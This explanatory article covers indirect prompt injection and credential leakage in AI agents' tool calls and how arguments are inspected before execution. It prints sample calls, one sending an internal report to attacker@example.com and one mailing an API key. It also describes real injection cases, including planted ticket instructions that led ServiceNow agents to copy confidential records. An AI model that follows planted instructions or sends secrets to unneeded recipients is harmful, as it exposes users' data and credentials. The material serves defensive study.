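# Prompt injection and credential leakage in AI agents' tool calls, and the inspection of tool arguments before execution

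## How an agent calls a tool, and where its secrets sit

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools, which are functions for jobs such as sending email, reading files, querying a database or fetching a web page. The model produces only text. A program around it, called the harness, holds the permissions and turns that text into actions. Developers now connect agents to mailboxes, code repositories and company databases, which has brought two security problems. Indirect prompt injection is an attack in which text that the agent reads while working, and that its user did not write, steers what the agent does. Credential leakage is the exposure of a password, key or access token to a recipient or channel that the task neither declares nor needs. Either can show up in a tool call's arguments, which are the values the model fills in. Many defences therefore examine a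 call after the model writes it and before the harness executes it, a practice known as runtime inspection. How much this inspection can detect depends on how the call is produced and where the agent's secrets are stored.

### One request, step by step

Without tools, a model suggests a list of steps and the user carries them out one by one, such as opening the calendar, creating the ticket and sending the email (Granados, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, 2026). With tools, a user can write "Summarise this web page and email the summary to my boss" and leave the rest to the agent. Fan, Li and colleagues (2026) base their argument in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* on a request like this, and most of the examples below start from it.

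The harness first sends the model the user's message together with a list of the available tools. Each entry gives a tool's name, a description in ordinary language and a schema, which sets out the arguments the tool takes and the type of each. The model replies with a request for a tool, in this case one that fetches the web page. The harness reads the request, fetches the page and sends the result to the model. The model keeps no record between these exchanges, so the harness sends the whole conversation again each time, including the original request, the model's own reply and the tool's output. The model then writes a second request, this time for the tool that sends email:

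```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "recipient": "boss@company.com",
    "body": "Here is a summary of the page: ..."
  }
}
```

The harness sends the email and returns the result to the model, which then writes a short answer to the user. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes this loop for developers building on its Claude models and notes that "the model never runs anything on its own."

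The block above is a tool call, which consists of the name of a tool and a set of arguments. Vendors' formats differ a little. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* describes a format in which a call also has an identifier that matches it to its result, and the arguments are labelled "input". *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026), a paper on authorising agents' actions, defines a candidate call as a pair c = (τ, θ), where τ is the tool and θ its structured arguments. Execute(c) is a separate event that occurs when the call reaches the real tool. Until then the call is only data, so a program can read it, compare it with a rule and refuse it.

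The schema alone gives little protection. It can require the recipient to be a well-formed email address, but an attacker's address is well formed too. The schema constrains a very general tool even less. A tool that runs shell commands may take a single string, and the commands in it can do anything the user's account can do.

Some calls also bypass the developer's harness. Anthropic offers versions of web search, page fetching and code execution that run on its own servers. The developer's application normally receives those calls only after they have finished, so a check inside it comes too late to stop them.

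### One shared context, and what skills and MCP add to it

At each step the model reads its context, a single sequence of text containing the developer's standing instructions, the tool descriptions, the user's request and every tool result so far. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, trace prompt injection to this arrangement, since language models operate directly on text and have no formal way to tell instructions from data. An instruction hidden in the fetched page reaches the model by the same route as the user's own words. The shared context also exposes secrets, because once a tool result containing a password enters it, the harness sends that result to the model at every later step, and the model can copy the password into any argument it writes.

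Skills widen the range of text that enters the context. A skill is a folder of instructions, scripts and other resources for a particular kind of work, such as filling in PDF forms. Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* describes how an agent loads a skill in stages. At startup, the context receives only the name and description of each installed skill. If a skill looks relevant, the agent reads its main file, SKILL.md, in full, and opens other files only when it needs them. Scripts in the folder can run without their code entering the context. Anthropic published the format as an open standard in December 2025, and third parties now supply skills in large numbers. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, counted 170,226 on a single marketplace in February 2026. A skill's author can therefore put instructions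 in front of the model and code on the user's machine. Anthropic warns that a malicious skill may direct the model to send data out, and recommends that users install skills only from trusted sources and audit the rest. Skills also make tool calls harder to inspect, because a script can make its own network requests while the call that launches it may show only the script's name.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in 2024, is an open standard for connecting agents to tools that other parties run. Each provider operates a server, and the harness connects to it through a component called a client. Under the current specification (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026), the client sends a `tools/list` request and receives names, descriptions and schemas, which the harness puts before the model. When the model chooses a tool, the client sends a `tools/call` request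 with the name and arguments. When the project released this version in July, it reported close to half a billion downloads a month for its main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The common format makes inspection easier, because one program can read calls to thousands of different tools, but it also means that outsiders write some of the tool descriptions in the agent's context.

Since the July version, calls sent over the web have carried the tool's name in a header, so that a gateway can route and authorise them without opening the message body. The arguments normally stay in the body, so a gateway that reads only headers can identify a call to an email tool but not the email's recipient. Servers may mark individual arguments for copying into headers too, but Model Context Protocol advises against marking passwords, keys or tokens, because intermediaries on the network can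 read header values. The same document recommends, but does not require, that clients show a tool's inputs to the user before calling the server, to avoid "malicious or accidental data exfiltration".

### What a credential is and where an agent meets one

A credential is a secret that proves identity or grants access. Chen and colleagues sort those they observed in skills into nine types:

- API keys and cloud credentials, which identify a program to an online service
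- OAuth tokens, which give an application limited access to someone's account without the password
- database logins
- passwords and passphrases
- private keys for secure connections
- encryption keys
- session and bearer tokens
- webhook secrets, with which a service verifies that an incoming message is genuine
- the keys and recovery phrases of cryptocurrency wallets

Some secrets are easy to recognise by their prefixes, such as "sk-" for certain API keys and "AKIA" for some Amazon cloud keys. A password, however, can look like any other word.

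Bearer tokens show most clearly why a leaked credential does damage. *RFC 6750* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the standard for using such tokens on the web, defines a bearer token as one that any party holding it can use in any way that any other holder can, without proving possession of a cryptographic key. A copy therefore works as well as the original, and the server cannot tell a thief from the owner by the token alone. Whoever obtains a leaked token can keep reading, writing or deleting whatever it covers until it expires or its issuer revokes it. An ordinary API key usually works the same way.

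Environment variables and configuration files are two of the four main places where an agent meets credentials. Environment variables are named values that the operating system gives a program when it starts, and developers often keep keys in them. Developers also keep keys in configuration files on disk, commonly under names such as `.env` or `.aws/credentials`. Chen and colleagues note that many skill frameworks run directly in the user's local environment, so an installed skill inherits access to both without anyone approving each credential. Security researchers call this ambient authority. At this stage the agent's programs can read the secret, but it is not yet in the model's context. It enters the context when the agent opens the file with a reading tool, or when a script prints the value, because agent frameworks commonly feed printed output back to the model.

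The third place is the request header. A program that presents a bearer token to a web service normally puts it in a header line that begins "Authorization: Bearer". Jones and Hardt recommend putting the token in the header rather than the web address because servers and other software are likely to log addresses, including any tokens in them. If the model composes the request itself, the token has to appear in the tool call's arguments, and its presence there is legitimate.

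The last place secrets sit is in text that users paste into the conversation. Users paste keys so that a task can proceed, sometimes because a skill's instructions tell them to, and a key is in the context as soon as the user sends it. Chen and colleagues searched skill descriptions for phrases such as "to continue, paste your API key here", which they class as social engineering.

### Four example calls

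Four example calls illustrate the situations that a check has to distinguish. Calls A, B and C arise from the request to summarise a web page and email the summary to the boss. Call D comes from a separate task, in which a user asks for the open issues in a software project on a code-hosting service.

```text
A  send_email(
     recipient = "boss@company.com",
     body      = "Here is a summary of the page: ...")

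B  send_email(
     recipient = "attacker@example.com",
     body      = "Internal report, third quarter: ...")

C  send_email(
     recipient = "boss@company.com",
     body      = "Here is a summary of the page: ...
                  API_KEY=sk-...")

D  http_request(
     url     = "https://api.codehost.example/issues",
     headers = {"Authorization": "Bearer ghp_..."})
```

Call A does what the user wanted. Its body is a summary, so text from an outside web page determines much of it.

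An attacker causes call B by placing text on the page that human visitors don't see, instructing the agent to send an internal report to an outside address. The agent can comply because it has access to the company's files. The report contains no password or key, but sending it to that address causes harm.

Call C has the right recipient, but its body contains an API key from a configuration file the agent read along the way. The agent may have included the key by accident or by following an instruction on the page, and the arguments would look the same in either case. Even if the boss is trustworthy, the key should not be in a mailbox, because anyone who later gains access to that mailbox can use it.

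Call D also contains a live credential, but the code host issued that token and needs it to answer the request.

Calls A and D should run and B and C should not, but crude rules fail on this set. Fan and colleagues show why for A and B. A rule that blocks an email whenever any argument depends on the web page stops A as well as B, while a rule that lets the page influence the whole call allows both. The difference, they say, is the recipient, which they call an authority-bearing argument because it decides where the action goes, whereas the body is content. C and D pose a similar problem for secrets, since a rule against any credential in any argument stops the legitimate request in D as well as the leak in C.

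### How researchers measure attacks and defences

Much of the evidence on prompt injection comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues built. It has four simulated environments (office software, the messaging service Slack, travel booking and banking) filled with invented emails, files and transactions. Each environment has user tasks, such as counting the day's appointments, and injection tasks, such as sending a security code to the attacker. The benchmark pairs every user task with every injection task in the same environment. The original version had 40 × 6 pairs for office software, 21 × 5 for Slack, 20 × 7 for travel and 16 × 9 for banking, 629 in all. For each pair, the benchmark inserts the attacker's text into material that the agent will read while doing the user's task, such as an email. When the agent has finished, ordinary program code checks the state of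 the environment to determine whether each of the two tasks succeeded. The designers did not use a language model to judge the results because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge. The benchmark is still in use. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) gives its size as over 900 pairs, and *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) reports runs on 13 models from six providers.

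Attack success rate is the share of attack attempts in which the attacker's goal is reached. Benign utility is the share of ordinary tasks that the agent completes when nobody is attacking. Both measures are needed because an agent that refuses every call has an attack success rate of zero but is useless. A low attack success rate can also reflect an incompetent agent. In their 2024 tests, Debenedetti and colleagues found that weaker models were often harder to attack, and suggested that these models failed to carry out the attacker's task even after the injection had redirected them. AgentDojo's attack success rate also excludes accidents, such as the key in call C leaking with no attacker involved, because there is no attacker's goal to score.

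A false positive is a harmless call, such as A or D, that a check blocks or holds. Researchers count false positives per call and benign utility per task, so a small false-positive rate can affect a large share of tasks. Some AgentDojo tasks need as many as 18 tool calls. If a check blocked one harmless call in a hundred, independently each time, an 18-call task would be blocked at least once with probability 1 − 0.99¹⁸, or about 17 per cent.

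## Prompt injection as unauthorised control of a tool call

The attacker behind call B has no access to the user's account or to the harness, but decides where the agent sends an email. In this sense, prompt injection lets an attacker control a tool without permission to use it.

### Direct and indirect injection

In direct prompt injection, the attacker's text reaches the model as part of the user's input. Call B is an indirect injection because the attacker's text comes from a web page.

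The direct form became known first, when Jonathan Cefalu of the AI security company Preamble reported it to OpenAI in May 2022 as "command injection". A Twitter user wrote of "prompt injection" later that month, and the programmer Simon Willison popularised the name in September. Applications of the time often placed a user's text after a fixed instruction, such as one to translate it into French. If the text contained its own instruction, the model might follow that instead. In February 2023, a Stanford student used direct injection to make Microsoft's Bing Chat reveal its internal guidelines. The same month, *Not What You've Signed Up For* (Greshake et al., 2023) described the indirect form and reported successful attacks on several models, including GPT-4.

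Direct and indirect injection usually have different victims. A user who injects directly works against the developer, whose instructions the model is supposed to follow. In indirect injection, an outsider works against the user, who has made an ordinary request and may never see the planted text. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, classifies attackers by the access they have when the attack runs. An "external adversary" can only alter material that the agent may retrieve, while a "user-level adversary" can write into the agent's input, sometimes by adding text to an innocent user's message. Such additions complicate runtime inspection because a check may use the user's message to determine what the agent is allowed to do. If a user pastes in a paragraph that contains planted instructions, the check may treat them as the user's own.

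### Jailbreaks, SQL injection and ordinary mistakes

Jailbreaking means getting a model to produce something its developer trained it to refuse, such as instructions for making a weapon. An injected call need not be objectionable in itself. Sending email is the normal use of an email tool, and call B would be harmless if the user had asked for it. Training a model to refuse dangerous requests therefore gives limited protection against injection, although an attacker can combine injection with jailbreaking.

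Prompt injection is named after SQL injection, an older attack on programs that query databases in the language SQL. If a program inserts a visitor's text directly into a query as a value, a quotation mark in that text can end the value early, so that the database runs the rest as a command. Programmers prevent this by sending the command and the values separately. Language models have no equivalent safeguard, because instructions and data share a single context. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre warned in December 2025 that developers may never be able to mitigate prompt injection as fully as SQL injection.

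*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) identifies another difference. A database's parser follows fixed rules, so the attacker has to supply exactly the right punctuation, whereas inexact marks can also work on a language model because it interprets punctuation probabilistically. Many tools "escape" the quotation marks in outside text, which tells a parser to treat them as ordinary characters, but the researchers found that models could still take the escaped marks for the end of a field.

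An agent can also send a message to the wrong person with no attacker involved, and the log may look the same as it would after an attack. Telling the two apart requires a more precise definition of an unauthorised call.

### The confused deputy

The underlying problem is older than language models. In 1988 the computer scientist Norm Hardy described an incident with a compiler on a commercial computer that many customers shared. The compiler had permission to write in a system directory because it kept usage statistics there. Customers could name a file to receive its debugging output. One customer named the billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote the billing records. The customer did not have permission to change that file, but the operating system checked only the compiler's permissions, which allowed it. Hardy used the term "confused deputy" for such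 a program, which works for two parties and uses authority from one to carry out a request from the other.

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* compares an agent under injection to Hardy's compiler. The agent has the user's permission to send email, and the web page supplies a recipient. The mail server checks only whether the agent may send from this account, so both call A and call B pass.

### Induced calls and permitted calls

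The same paper defines an attack in a way that distinguishes it from a mistake and from the normal use of outside information. Let U be the user's request, X the legitimate work done so far, O a tool result the agent has read, and c the call the agent now proposes.

```text
Induced(c, O)  does not imply  Permitted(c, given U and X)

Violation  =  Execute(c)  and  not Permitted(c, given U and X)
```

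A tool result induces a call if it helps cause the call. A call is permitted if the request and the work so far authorise it. A violation occurs when an unauthorised call reaches the real tool. If an untrusted tool result induced the call, the violation is a successful injection. A call that an agent makes by its own mistake, without outside text inducing it, can also be a violation.

In the paper's test case, a user asks an agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. The agent's search returns the file's identifier, which the user could not have supplied in advance. The same search result also contains an instruction to send a copy to attacker@example.com. Outside text influences both emails. In the email to Alice, it fills in a detail of the user's request, which the paper calls runtime instantiation. The copy to the attacker would add a recipient the user never mentioned,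 which the paper calls authority expansion. Tool results may supply the objects, identifiers and facts that a task needs, but they may not by themselves add operations, targets, recipients, permissions or outside effects.

Call C shows a practical advantage of the definition, which is that a check does not have to determine whether an attack took place to identify a violation. Neither the request nor the work done for it authorised mailing the key, so the call is a violation whether the key was included by accident or because of an instruction on the page. The paper's monitor, SARA, applies this distinction to calls before they run.

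There is no mechanical test for "permitted", because it depends on what a user meant by one or two sentences. The paper excludes cases in which a user tells the agent to carry out whatever a document says, because the user has then chosen to let the document's contents determine what the agent does. Many requests come close to that. When a user writes "pay the attached invoice", the agent has to take the payee, account number and amount from the invoice, and a payment to the account printed there is permitted. If the invoice is forged, the attacker gets the money without having given the agent any instruction.

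### False data without an instruction

Choi and colleagues show that attackers can exploit this gap systematically. They call the technique agent data injection. They divide the data in an agent's context into trusted data, which the tool itself generates, and untrusted data, which outsiders can write. In an email, the sender's address is trusted because the mail service fills it in, while the subject and body are untrusted. Writing I for the instructions, T for trusted data, U for untrusted data and A for the attacker's text, the paper contrasts two attacks:

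```text
instruction injection:   LLM(I, (T, U + A))  ≈  LLM(I + A, (T, U))
data injection:          LLM(I, (T, U + A))  ≈  LLM(I, (T + A, U))
```

The left-hand sides are the same because in both attacks the attacker can write only to untrusted fields. In instruction injection, the model behaves almost as if the attacker's text were part of its instructions. In data injection, it behaves almost as if a trusted tool had supplied the text, and it continues the user's task using false facts.

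The attacker does this by imitating the layout of the data. In one example, the body of the attacker's email contains text made to look like the end of that message and the start of another from Alice. The mail tool handles one email, but the model interprets it as two. The researchers used the same principle against commercial products, including Claude in Chrome, Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. Fake elements on web pages led browsing agents to click where the attacker wanted. On GitHub, a service where programmers share code and discuss faults, an attacker's comment appeared to come from a project's maintainer, and coding agents ran the commands in it. Anthropic, OpenAI and Google acknowledged the reports.

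In tests of six models outside an agent, the imitation succeeded in 31.3 to 43.3 per cent of attempts on JSON, the format of the example calls above, and in 33.3 to 100 per cent on web page data. Against agents with current defences, instruction injection succeeded in at most 0.7 per cent of attempts, and data injection in up to 50 per cent. Most of those defences try to stop outside text from acting as an instruction, which it never does in data injection. Comparing the call with the user's request may not help either. If a user asks an agent to apply the maintainer's fix, a call that applies a fix falsely presented as the maintainer's looks like what the user wanted.

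### What the attacker steers

An injection can change which tool the agent calls. For example, a user might ask only for a summary of a web page, and an injection might make the agent try to send an email. The harness can stop this call by limiting the agent to the tools that the task needs. This does not work in the running example, because the user's request needs the email tool.

Call B uses the same tool but changes an authority-bearing argument, the recipient. An attacker can also target the content by putting false claims on a page so that they might end up in the summary, which the boss then receives from a trusted colleague. A check on this call would find very little evidence of the attack, because the recipient is correct and the user did ask for a summary.

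Other attacks change the order or number of calls. Choi and colleagues put a fake tool response in a pull request, a proposal to change a project's code. The agent merged the change without reviewing the code. The merge call itself could look normal, because the fault was the missing review before it. In *CARI*, Fu, Wu and colleagues (2026) trapped coding agents in repeated rounds of debugging and testing. The agents used more than 2,000 times as many tokens (the units of text that models process) as they did for the same work without an attack. Coding agents routinely rerun tests, so only the history of the task shows that something is wrong.

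### Where the text enters

Web pages and emails are the most accessible route for prompt injection, because anyone can publish a page or send a message. The attacker then has to wait for an agent to read it.

The model receives tool descriptions before it starts work. The survey uses the term "tool poisoning" for planting instructions in a tool's name or description. A poisoned description can influence calls to other tools even if the agent never uses the poisoned tool. Skills give an attacker even more room to plant instructions, and the agent is supposed to follow the instructions a skill contains.

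Fu and colleagues studied prompt injection through the responses of live software. Their attacker controls one part of a shared project, such as a backend service or a test system, that another team member's coding agent has to work with. When the agent calls the service, the service returns an error message containing malicious advice on how to fix the problem. The service can legitimately report its own errors, but it has no authority over files and passwords on the team member's machine. The researchers call this "direct" injection because a live source delivers the text while the agent is working. The usual term is "indirect" injection, since the text does not come from the user.

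In the same study, agents received identical malicious text in one of three places: a stored debugging file, a log from the running program, or an error message returned after the agent's own action. With GPT-5.4-mini, the attack succeeded in 8.9 per cent of trials using the file, 35.6 per cent using the log and 93.3 per cent using the error message. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, the figures were 2.2, 57.8 and 97.8 per cent in the same order. A filter that checks only the wording would give the same result in all three places. Agents cannot simply ignore error messages, because responding to them is a large part of programming.

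### From one agent to another: the ServiceNow case

Text can also pass from one agent to the next. Aaron Costello, then chief of security research at AppOmni, demonstrated this in Now Assist, the AI product of the business software company ServiceNow. The Hacker News (2025) reported his findings in November. Agents in Now Assist can find and recruit one another when they cannot finish a task alone. According to AppOmni, the agents must use a language model that supports the feature, belong to the same team, and be set as discoverable. The default configuration met all these conditions.

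Costello gave an administrator two standard agents. One read and categorised support tickets, and the other could read, create and change records. He then created an ordinary user who could file tickets but not read other people's, and used that account to file one with instructions hidden in its description. When the first agent processed the ticket, it brought in the second agent, which copied the contents of a confidential ticket into the ordinary user's ticket. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was switched on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to send data out by email and give a user the administrator's role.

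By default, these agents act with the rights of the person who starts the interaction. The access rules correctly kept the ordinary user out of the confidential ticket, but the agents were working for an administrator, who could open it. The final call updated a ticket within the company's own system, so a search for suspicious outside addresses would have found nothing. Recognising the problem required knowing that the administrator had asked only for a ticket to be categorised, and that the second agent's task came from a stranger's text that the first agent had read.

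ServiceNow replied that the system was working as designed and updated its documentation. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* reported some months later that the feature was still on by default. Costello recommends that a person approve each use of powerful tools and that companies put harmless and powerful agents in separate teams. He concedes that human approval reduces the benefit of automation. AppOmni has a commercial interest in the problem because it sells a product that monitors these agents, but ServiceNow did not dispute the behaviour.

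### How often current models give way

The success rate of prompt injection depends heavily on how many attempts an attacker gets. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that, on an older test by the security firm Gray Swan, a single strong attack succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 in 4.7 per cent of cases. The rate rose to 33.6 per cent with ten attempts and 63 per cent with a hundred. Success also depends on the setting. VentureBeat reported that Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted all 200 attempts in a coding test. When the same model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time, and at least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6 per cent of the time.

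Newer models do much better. Anthropic's *System Card* for Claude Opus 5 (July 2026) gives results on a benchmark that Gray Swan built with the British and American governments' AI testing institutes and several developers. Participants in a public competition wrote the attacks, and the July version of the benchmark used 1,130 that had worked against a range of models, in 28 scenarios. An attacker's chance of success against Opus 5 was 0.2 per cent with one attempt and 2.0 per cent with fifteen, compared with 3.1 and 20.0 per cent against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic is reporting on its competitors here, and does not know what safeguards their public services included.

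By September Gray Swan had enlarged the benchmark to 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports an attack success rate of 0.1 per cent for one attempt and 1.0 per cent for fifteen. Nearly all the successes came from tasks on a graphical screen, and none from tasks with ordinary tools. The fifteen-attempt rate for Opus 5 rose from 2.0 per cent on the old version of the benchmark to 4.8 per cent on the new one, so results from different versions are not comparable. Even at a success rate of 0.1 per cent, an attacker who sent the same email to a thousand inboxes could expect to compromise about one of them.

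A benchmark of fixed attacks may flatter a model that has not met anything new. For its coding and computer-use tests, Anthropic therefore uses Shade, a Gray Swan tool that improves its attacks through practice on the test scenarios. Professional testers wrote the attacks for the browser test. The July results for Opus 5, with its extended reasoning switched on, were as follows:

| Setting | Scenarios × attempts | Successful attempts | Scenarios with a success | With added safeguards |
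|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 40 × 200 | 0.56% | 13 of 40 | 0.18%, 4 of 40 |
| Computer use | 14 × 200 | 0.54% | 1 of 14 | 0.25%, 1 of 14 |
| Web browser | 129 × 10 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |

If every coding attempt had the same 0.56 per cent chance, 200 attempts would succeed at least once in about 67 per cent of scenarios (1 − 0.9944²⁰⁰), or 27 of the 40. The actual number was 13, so the successes were concentrated in a minority of scenarios where the model was weaker. In the coding and computer-use tests, the safeguards were classifiers that examine tool results before the model acts on them. The browser test added a classifier that can block outgoing calls, so that row's zero applies to the combination. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports the zero alongside OpenAI's admission that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

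Anthropic considers the Shade tests harsher than real conditions, because real attackers rarely get to practise on the exact task and risk discovery if they try repeatedly. But the coding test is lenient in one respect, because Gray Swan trains the attacker on earlier Claude models and runs it unchanged on new ones. Gray Swan has since trained a stronger attacker, and Anthropic reports that it succeeds at high rates.

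The September coding results also show that a safeguard against one danger can increase another. Shade succeeded in 9.26 per cent of attempts against Fable 5.1 and in 31 of the 40 scenarios, far more than against Opus 5 in July. Fable 5.1 has a classifier that checks requests for hacking misuse and passes suspicious ones to an older model, Opus 4.8, which handled 95 per cent of the requests that received a valid response. None of the 369 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack.

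Independent researchers have found much higher rates with other methods. Fu and colleagues tried ten attacks through live error messages on five models, in four programming languages, and succeeded in 2,845 of 3,000 trials, or 94.8 per cent. Against complete products, the rate was 61.3 per cent for Codex and 58.7 per cent for Claude Code. These rates may be higher than Anthropic's for several reasons. The models that Fu and colleagues name are older than Opus 5, and their attacks arrive in messages that the agent has to act on to finish its work. Some of the attacks aim to waste resources, a milder harm than the theft and destruction in Gray Swan's scenarios. Codex and Claude Code blocked several attacks that named sensitive commands or files outright, but many of those attacks succeeded when the researchers described the same actions in the ordinary language of debugging.

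## Credential leakage through tool arguments

Credential leakage differs from prompt injection in that it concerns who receives a secret rather than who controls a call, so an agent can leak a key with no attacker involved.

### What counts as a leak

Chen and colleagues define leakage as exposure to a recipient or channel that a skill's stated functionality neither declares nor needs. This covers careless exposure as well as theft. When an agent works without a skill, the user's request can take the place of the stated functionality.

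By this definition, call D is not a leak, but call C is, because neither the boss nor the company that runs the mail server needs the API key.

An agent also leaks a credential if it sends the token from call D to the code host's public status page, which reports outages. This leak is less obvious because the company already has the token, and it is usually less harmful than call C. But the status page has no use for the token, and an outside contractor may run that server and keep its logs. A rule that allows a credential to go anywhere within the right company is therefore too loose, and it must name the specific host.

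An agent might also paste a whole error message, including a token, into a web search. Even if the task requires a search, the query doesn't need to include the token. Detecting this leak requires inspecting the query's content, because the search tool sends every query to the same company and a check on recipients cannot catch it.

A password in a bug report is usually a leak too, since developers can investigate a failed login without it. An exception is a shared test account whose password the developers have circulated for this purpose. Even then, whether it is a leak depends on who can read the report, so it matters whether the issue tracker is public or private. Such mistakes were common before agents. GitGuardian (2025), which sells software for finding leaked secrets, reported credentials in 6.1 per cent of tickets in Jira, a system for tracking tasks and faults.

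Read literally, the definition allows a skill to send users' API keys to its author's statistics server as long as the skill declares the transfer. In practice, the researchers applied a stricter rule. If a skill regularly sent out credentials in normal use, they accepted it as benign only if the transfer was both declared and necessary. The stricter rule suits runtime inspection better, because an attacker who writes a skill also writes its declarations.

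### Context, arguments and logs

A secret can enter the model's context, leave in a tool argument, and remain in a log. Inspecting arguments covers only the second of these events. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) similarly distinguishes internal exposure, in which an agent only processes sensitive data, from leakage, in which the data crosses a trust boundary without authorisation. It treats harm as a further step, which occurs when someone exploits the data.

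When a model runs on a vendor's servers, a secret that enters its context has already left the user's machine. The Hacker News' *Grok Build Uploaded Entire Git Repositories to xAI Storage* (2026) describes a test of Grok Build, xAI's coding agent, in which a researcher writing as cereblab put a fake API key and database password in a `.env` file. When the agent read the file, it sent the contents to the model unredacted and put a second copy in an archive bound for xAI's storage.

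Grok Build also uploaded whole code repositories, including a file that the researcher had told the agent not to open. In one test, it sent about 192 KB to the model and 5.10 GiB to storage. The uploads stopped in cereblab's tests on July 13, after a change on xAI's servers. Other cloud coding agents also send the files they open, but Claude Code and Codex sent no copy of the repository in the same comparison. Inspecting tool arguments would not have revealed secrets in this traffic, because the argument of a file-reading call is only a file name and the surrounding program carries out the uploads.

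An experiment by the security company Dragos shows how attackers can obtain and use secrets sent to AI providers. From July to November 2026, a team led by HD Moore, its chief research officer, placed unique fake credentials and web addresses in nearly two million prompts and sent them to AI providers, according to Cybernews' *AI routers are leaking your passwords. Here's the proof*. UA.News' *Study finds secret leaks in AI service chains* adds that each secret went to one provider in one request, so any later use of it meant someone had seen that prompt. The team found signs of a compromise at three or more hosting providers. Attackers took a few hundred of the fake Amazon cloud keys, tried some of them within hours, and made tens of thousands of requests with them. They looked for stored files and more secrets, and tried to add user accounts to keep their access.

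Some of the exposed prompts carried a setting that tells providers not to retain data. As Moore put it, "a privacy flag only binds the first hop". His results apply mainly to intermediaries and the hosting companies behind them, and he recommends dealing directly with a major provider. ENTER.CO's *OpenRouter expulsa a tres proveedores de IA por filtrar prompts y claves* reports that the prompts travelled through OpenRouter, a service that passes requests on to many hosts. OpenRouter said its own systems had not failed, and removed three hosts. One hosting company, Together AI, said an AI coding agent had exposed a repository credential on GitHub, which let an outsider download stored prompts and any credentials in them. Dragos planted its secrets in prompts, not in tool arguments, so the experiment measures only what happens to the context.

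Logs can turn a harmless call into a leak after it has run. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, asks for permission before most shell commands. According to Anthropic's documentation, when a user first gives a standing approval, such as "Yes, and don't ask again", the program creates a settings file in the project folder to store it. If the approval covers one exact command, the file also stores any secret in that command. GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* gives an example in which the command fetches a project's closed issues from GitLab, with a dummy token in a header. This is call D as a shell command. The token ends up in a plain text file even though the recipient is correct and the user has approved the call.

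Many developers then published that file with their code. iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets* reports that the security firm Apiiro found 104,185 public copies on GitHub in early November 2026. Of these, 1,122 contained at least one secret. Apiiro counted 1,379 distinct secrets, more than a third of which were for direct database access, but did not test whether they worked. Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports that GitGuardian examined everything uploaded since January 2025 and found 31,088 distinct credentials, of which 5,343 worked when it detected them. The monthly number peaked at 12,535 in April 2026 and had fallen to 959 by October, for reasons GitGuardian could not identify.

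The companies disagree about the cause. Claude Code tells Git, the program that tracks and publishes code, to ignore the settings file, but that instruction isn't copied with the project to other computers. Boris Cherny, the head of Claude Code, argued that people must have created and published the exposed copies by hand. In all of the about 3,000 occurrences that GitGuardian reviewed, the secret was in a rule with exactly the form that the permission prompt writes. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* reports that Claude also had a part in publishing the files, having co-authored the change that touched the file in 539 of 1,105 affected projects. Cherny said his team was looking into ways to prevent the problem.

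### Accidental and induced leaks

A leak is induced if someone wrote text to cause it and the agent read that text. Otherwise it is accidental. The secrets in Claude Code's settings files leaked accidentally, because a developer could approve a command containing a password without anyone planting text for the agent to read.

TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes another accident, which the security vendor NordLayer observed with its monitoring product, AI Scout. A quality assurance engineer asked a coding assistant to review proposed code changes. The project's instructions were to take a GitLab token from a configuration file, which also held production passwords, a token for the human resources system and credentials for a business intelligence service. The assistant read the whole file in ten separate sessions over three weeks, sending its contents to an outside AI service each time.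 Later, in a fresh copy of the project without that file, it printed every environment variable on the computer, which exposed more passwords. It then noted that it had "leaked secrets into this session's tool output" and advised the engineer to replace them.

This account comes from NordLayer, which sells protection against such incidents, but the steps it describes are ordinary. The definition of leakage applies differently to the secrets in the file. The project's instructions called for the GitLab token, so its use was declared, but the task did not require the production passwords. A scan of the assistant's arguments for secrets would have found none, because the passwords arrived in the results of its calls. The arguments did contain other warning signs. In them, the assistant named a file known to hold credentials and later asked for all the environment variables.

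Agents can also choose an unsafe channel because the safe one is unavailable. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (2026) describes how developers asked agents to prove that user interface changes worked. GitHub accepts images for code reviews only through a browser, and the agents worked from a command line, so some posted the screenshots in public repositories. Researchers at Glow Labs found material from more than 300 organisations, including customer billing records. They reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code and the Opus 5 model on a test project, where the agent reasoned that the images had to be hosted somewhere and created a public repository for them. At one software vendor, more than a dozen agents saved the method as a skill and uploaded over a thousand screenshots and recordings within a week.

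A filter for planted instructions would have found nothing in any of these cases. Checking whether the task requires sending a secret to a given recipient could in principle catch both accidental and induced leaks, if the secret appears in the call.

### A leak in five stages

Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, divide a credential leak into five stages:

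1. Introduction: a reusable secret appears in a user's message, a prompt template, a source file or a tool's configuration.
2. Propagation: the system copies it into the context, conversation history, logs, memory, generated code or error messages.
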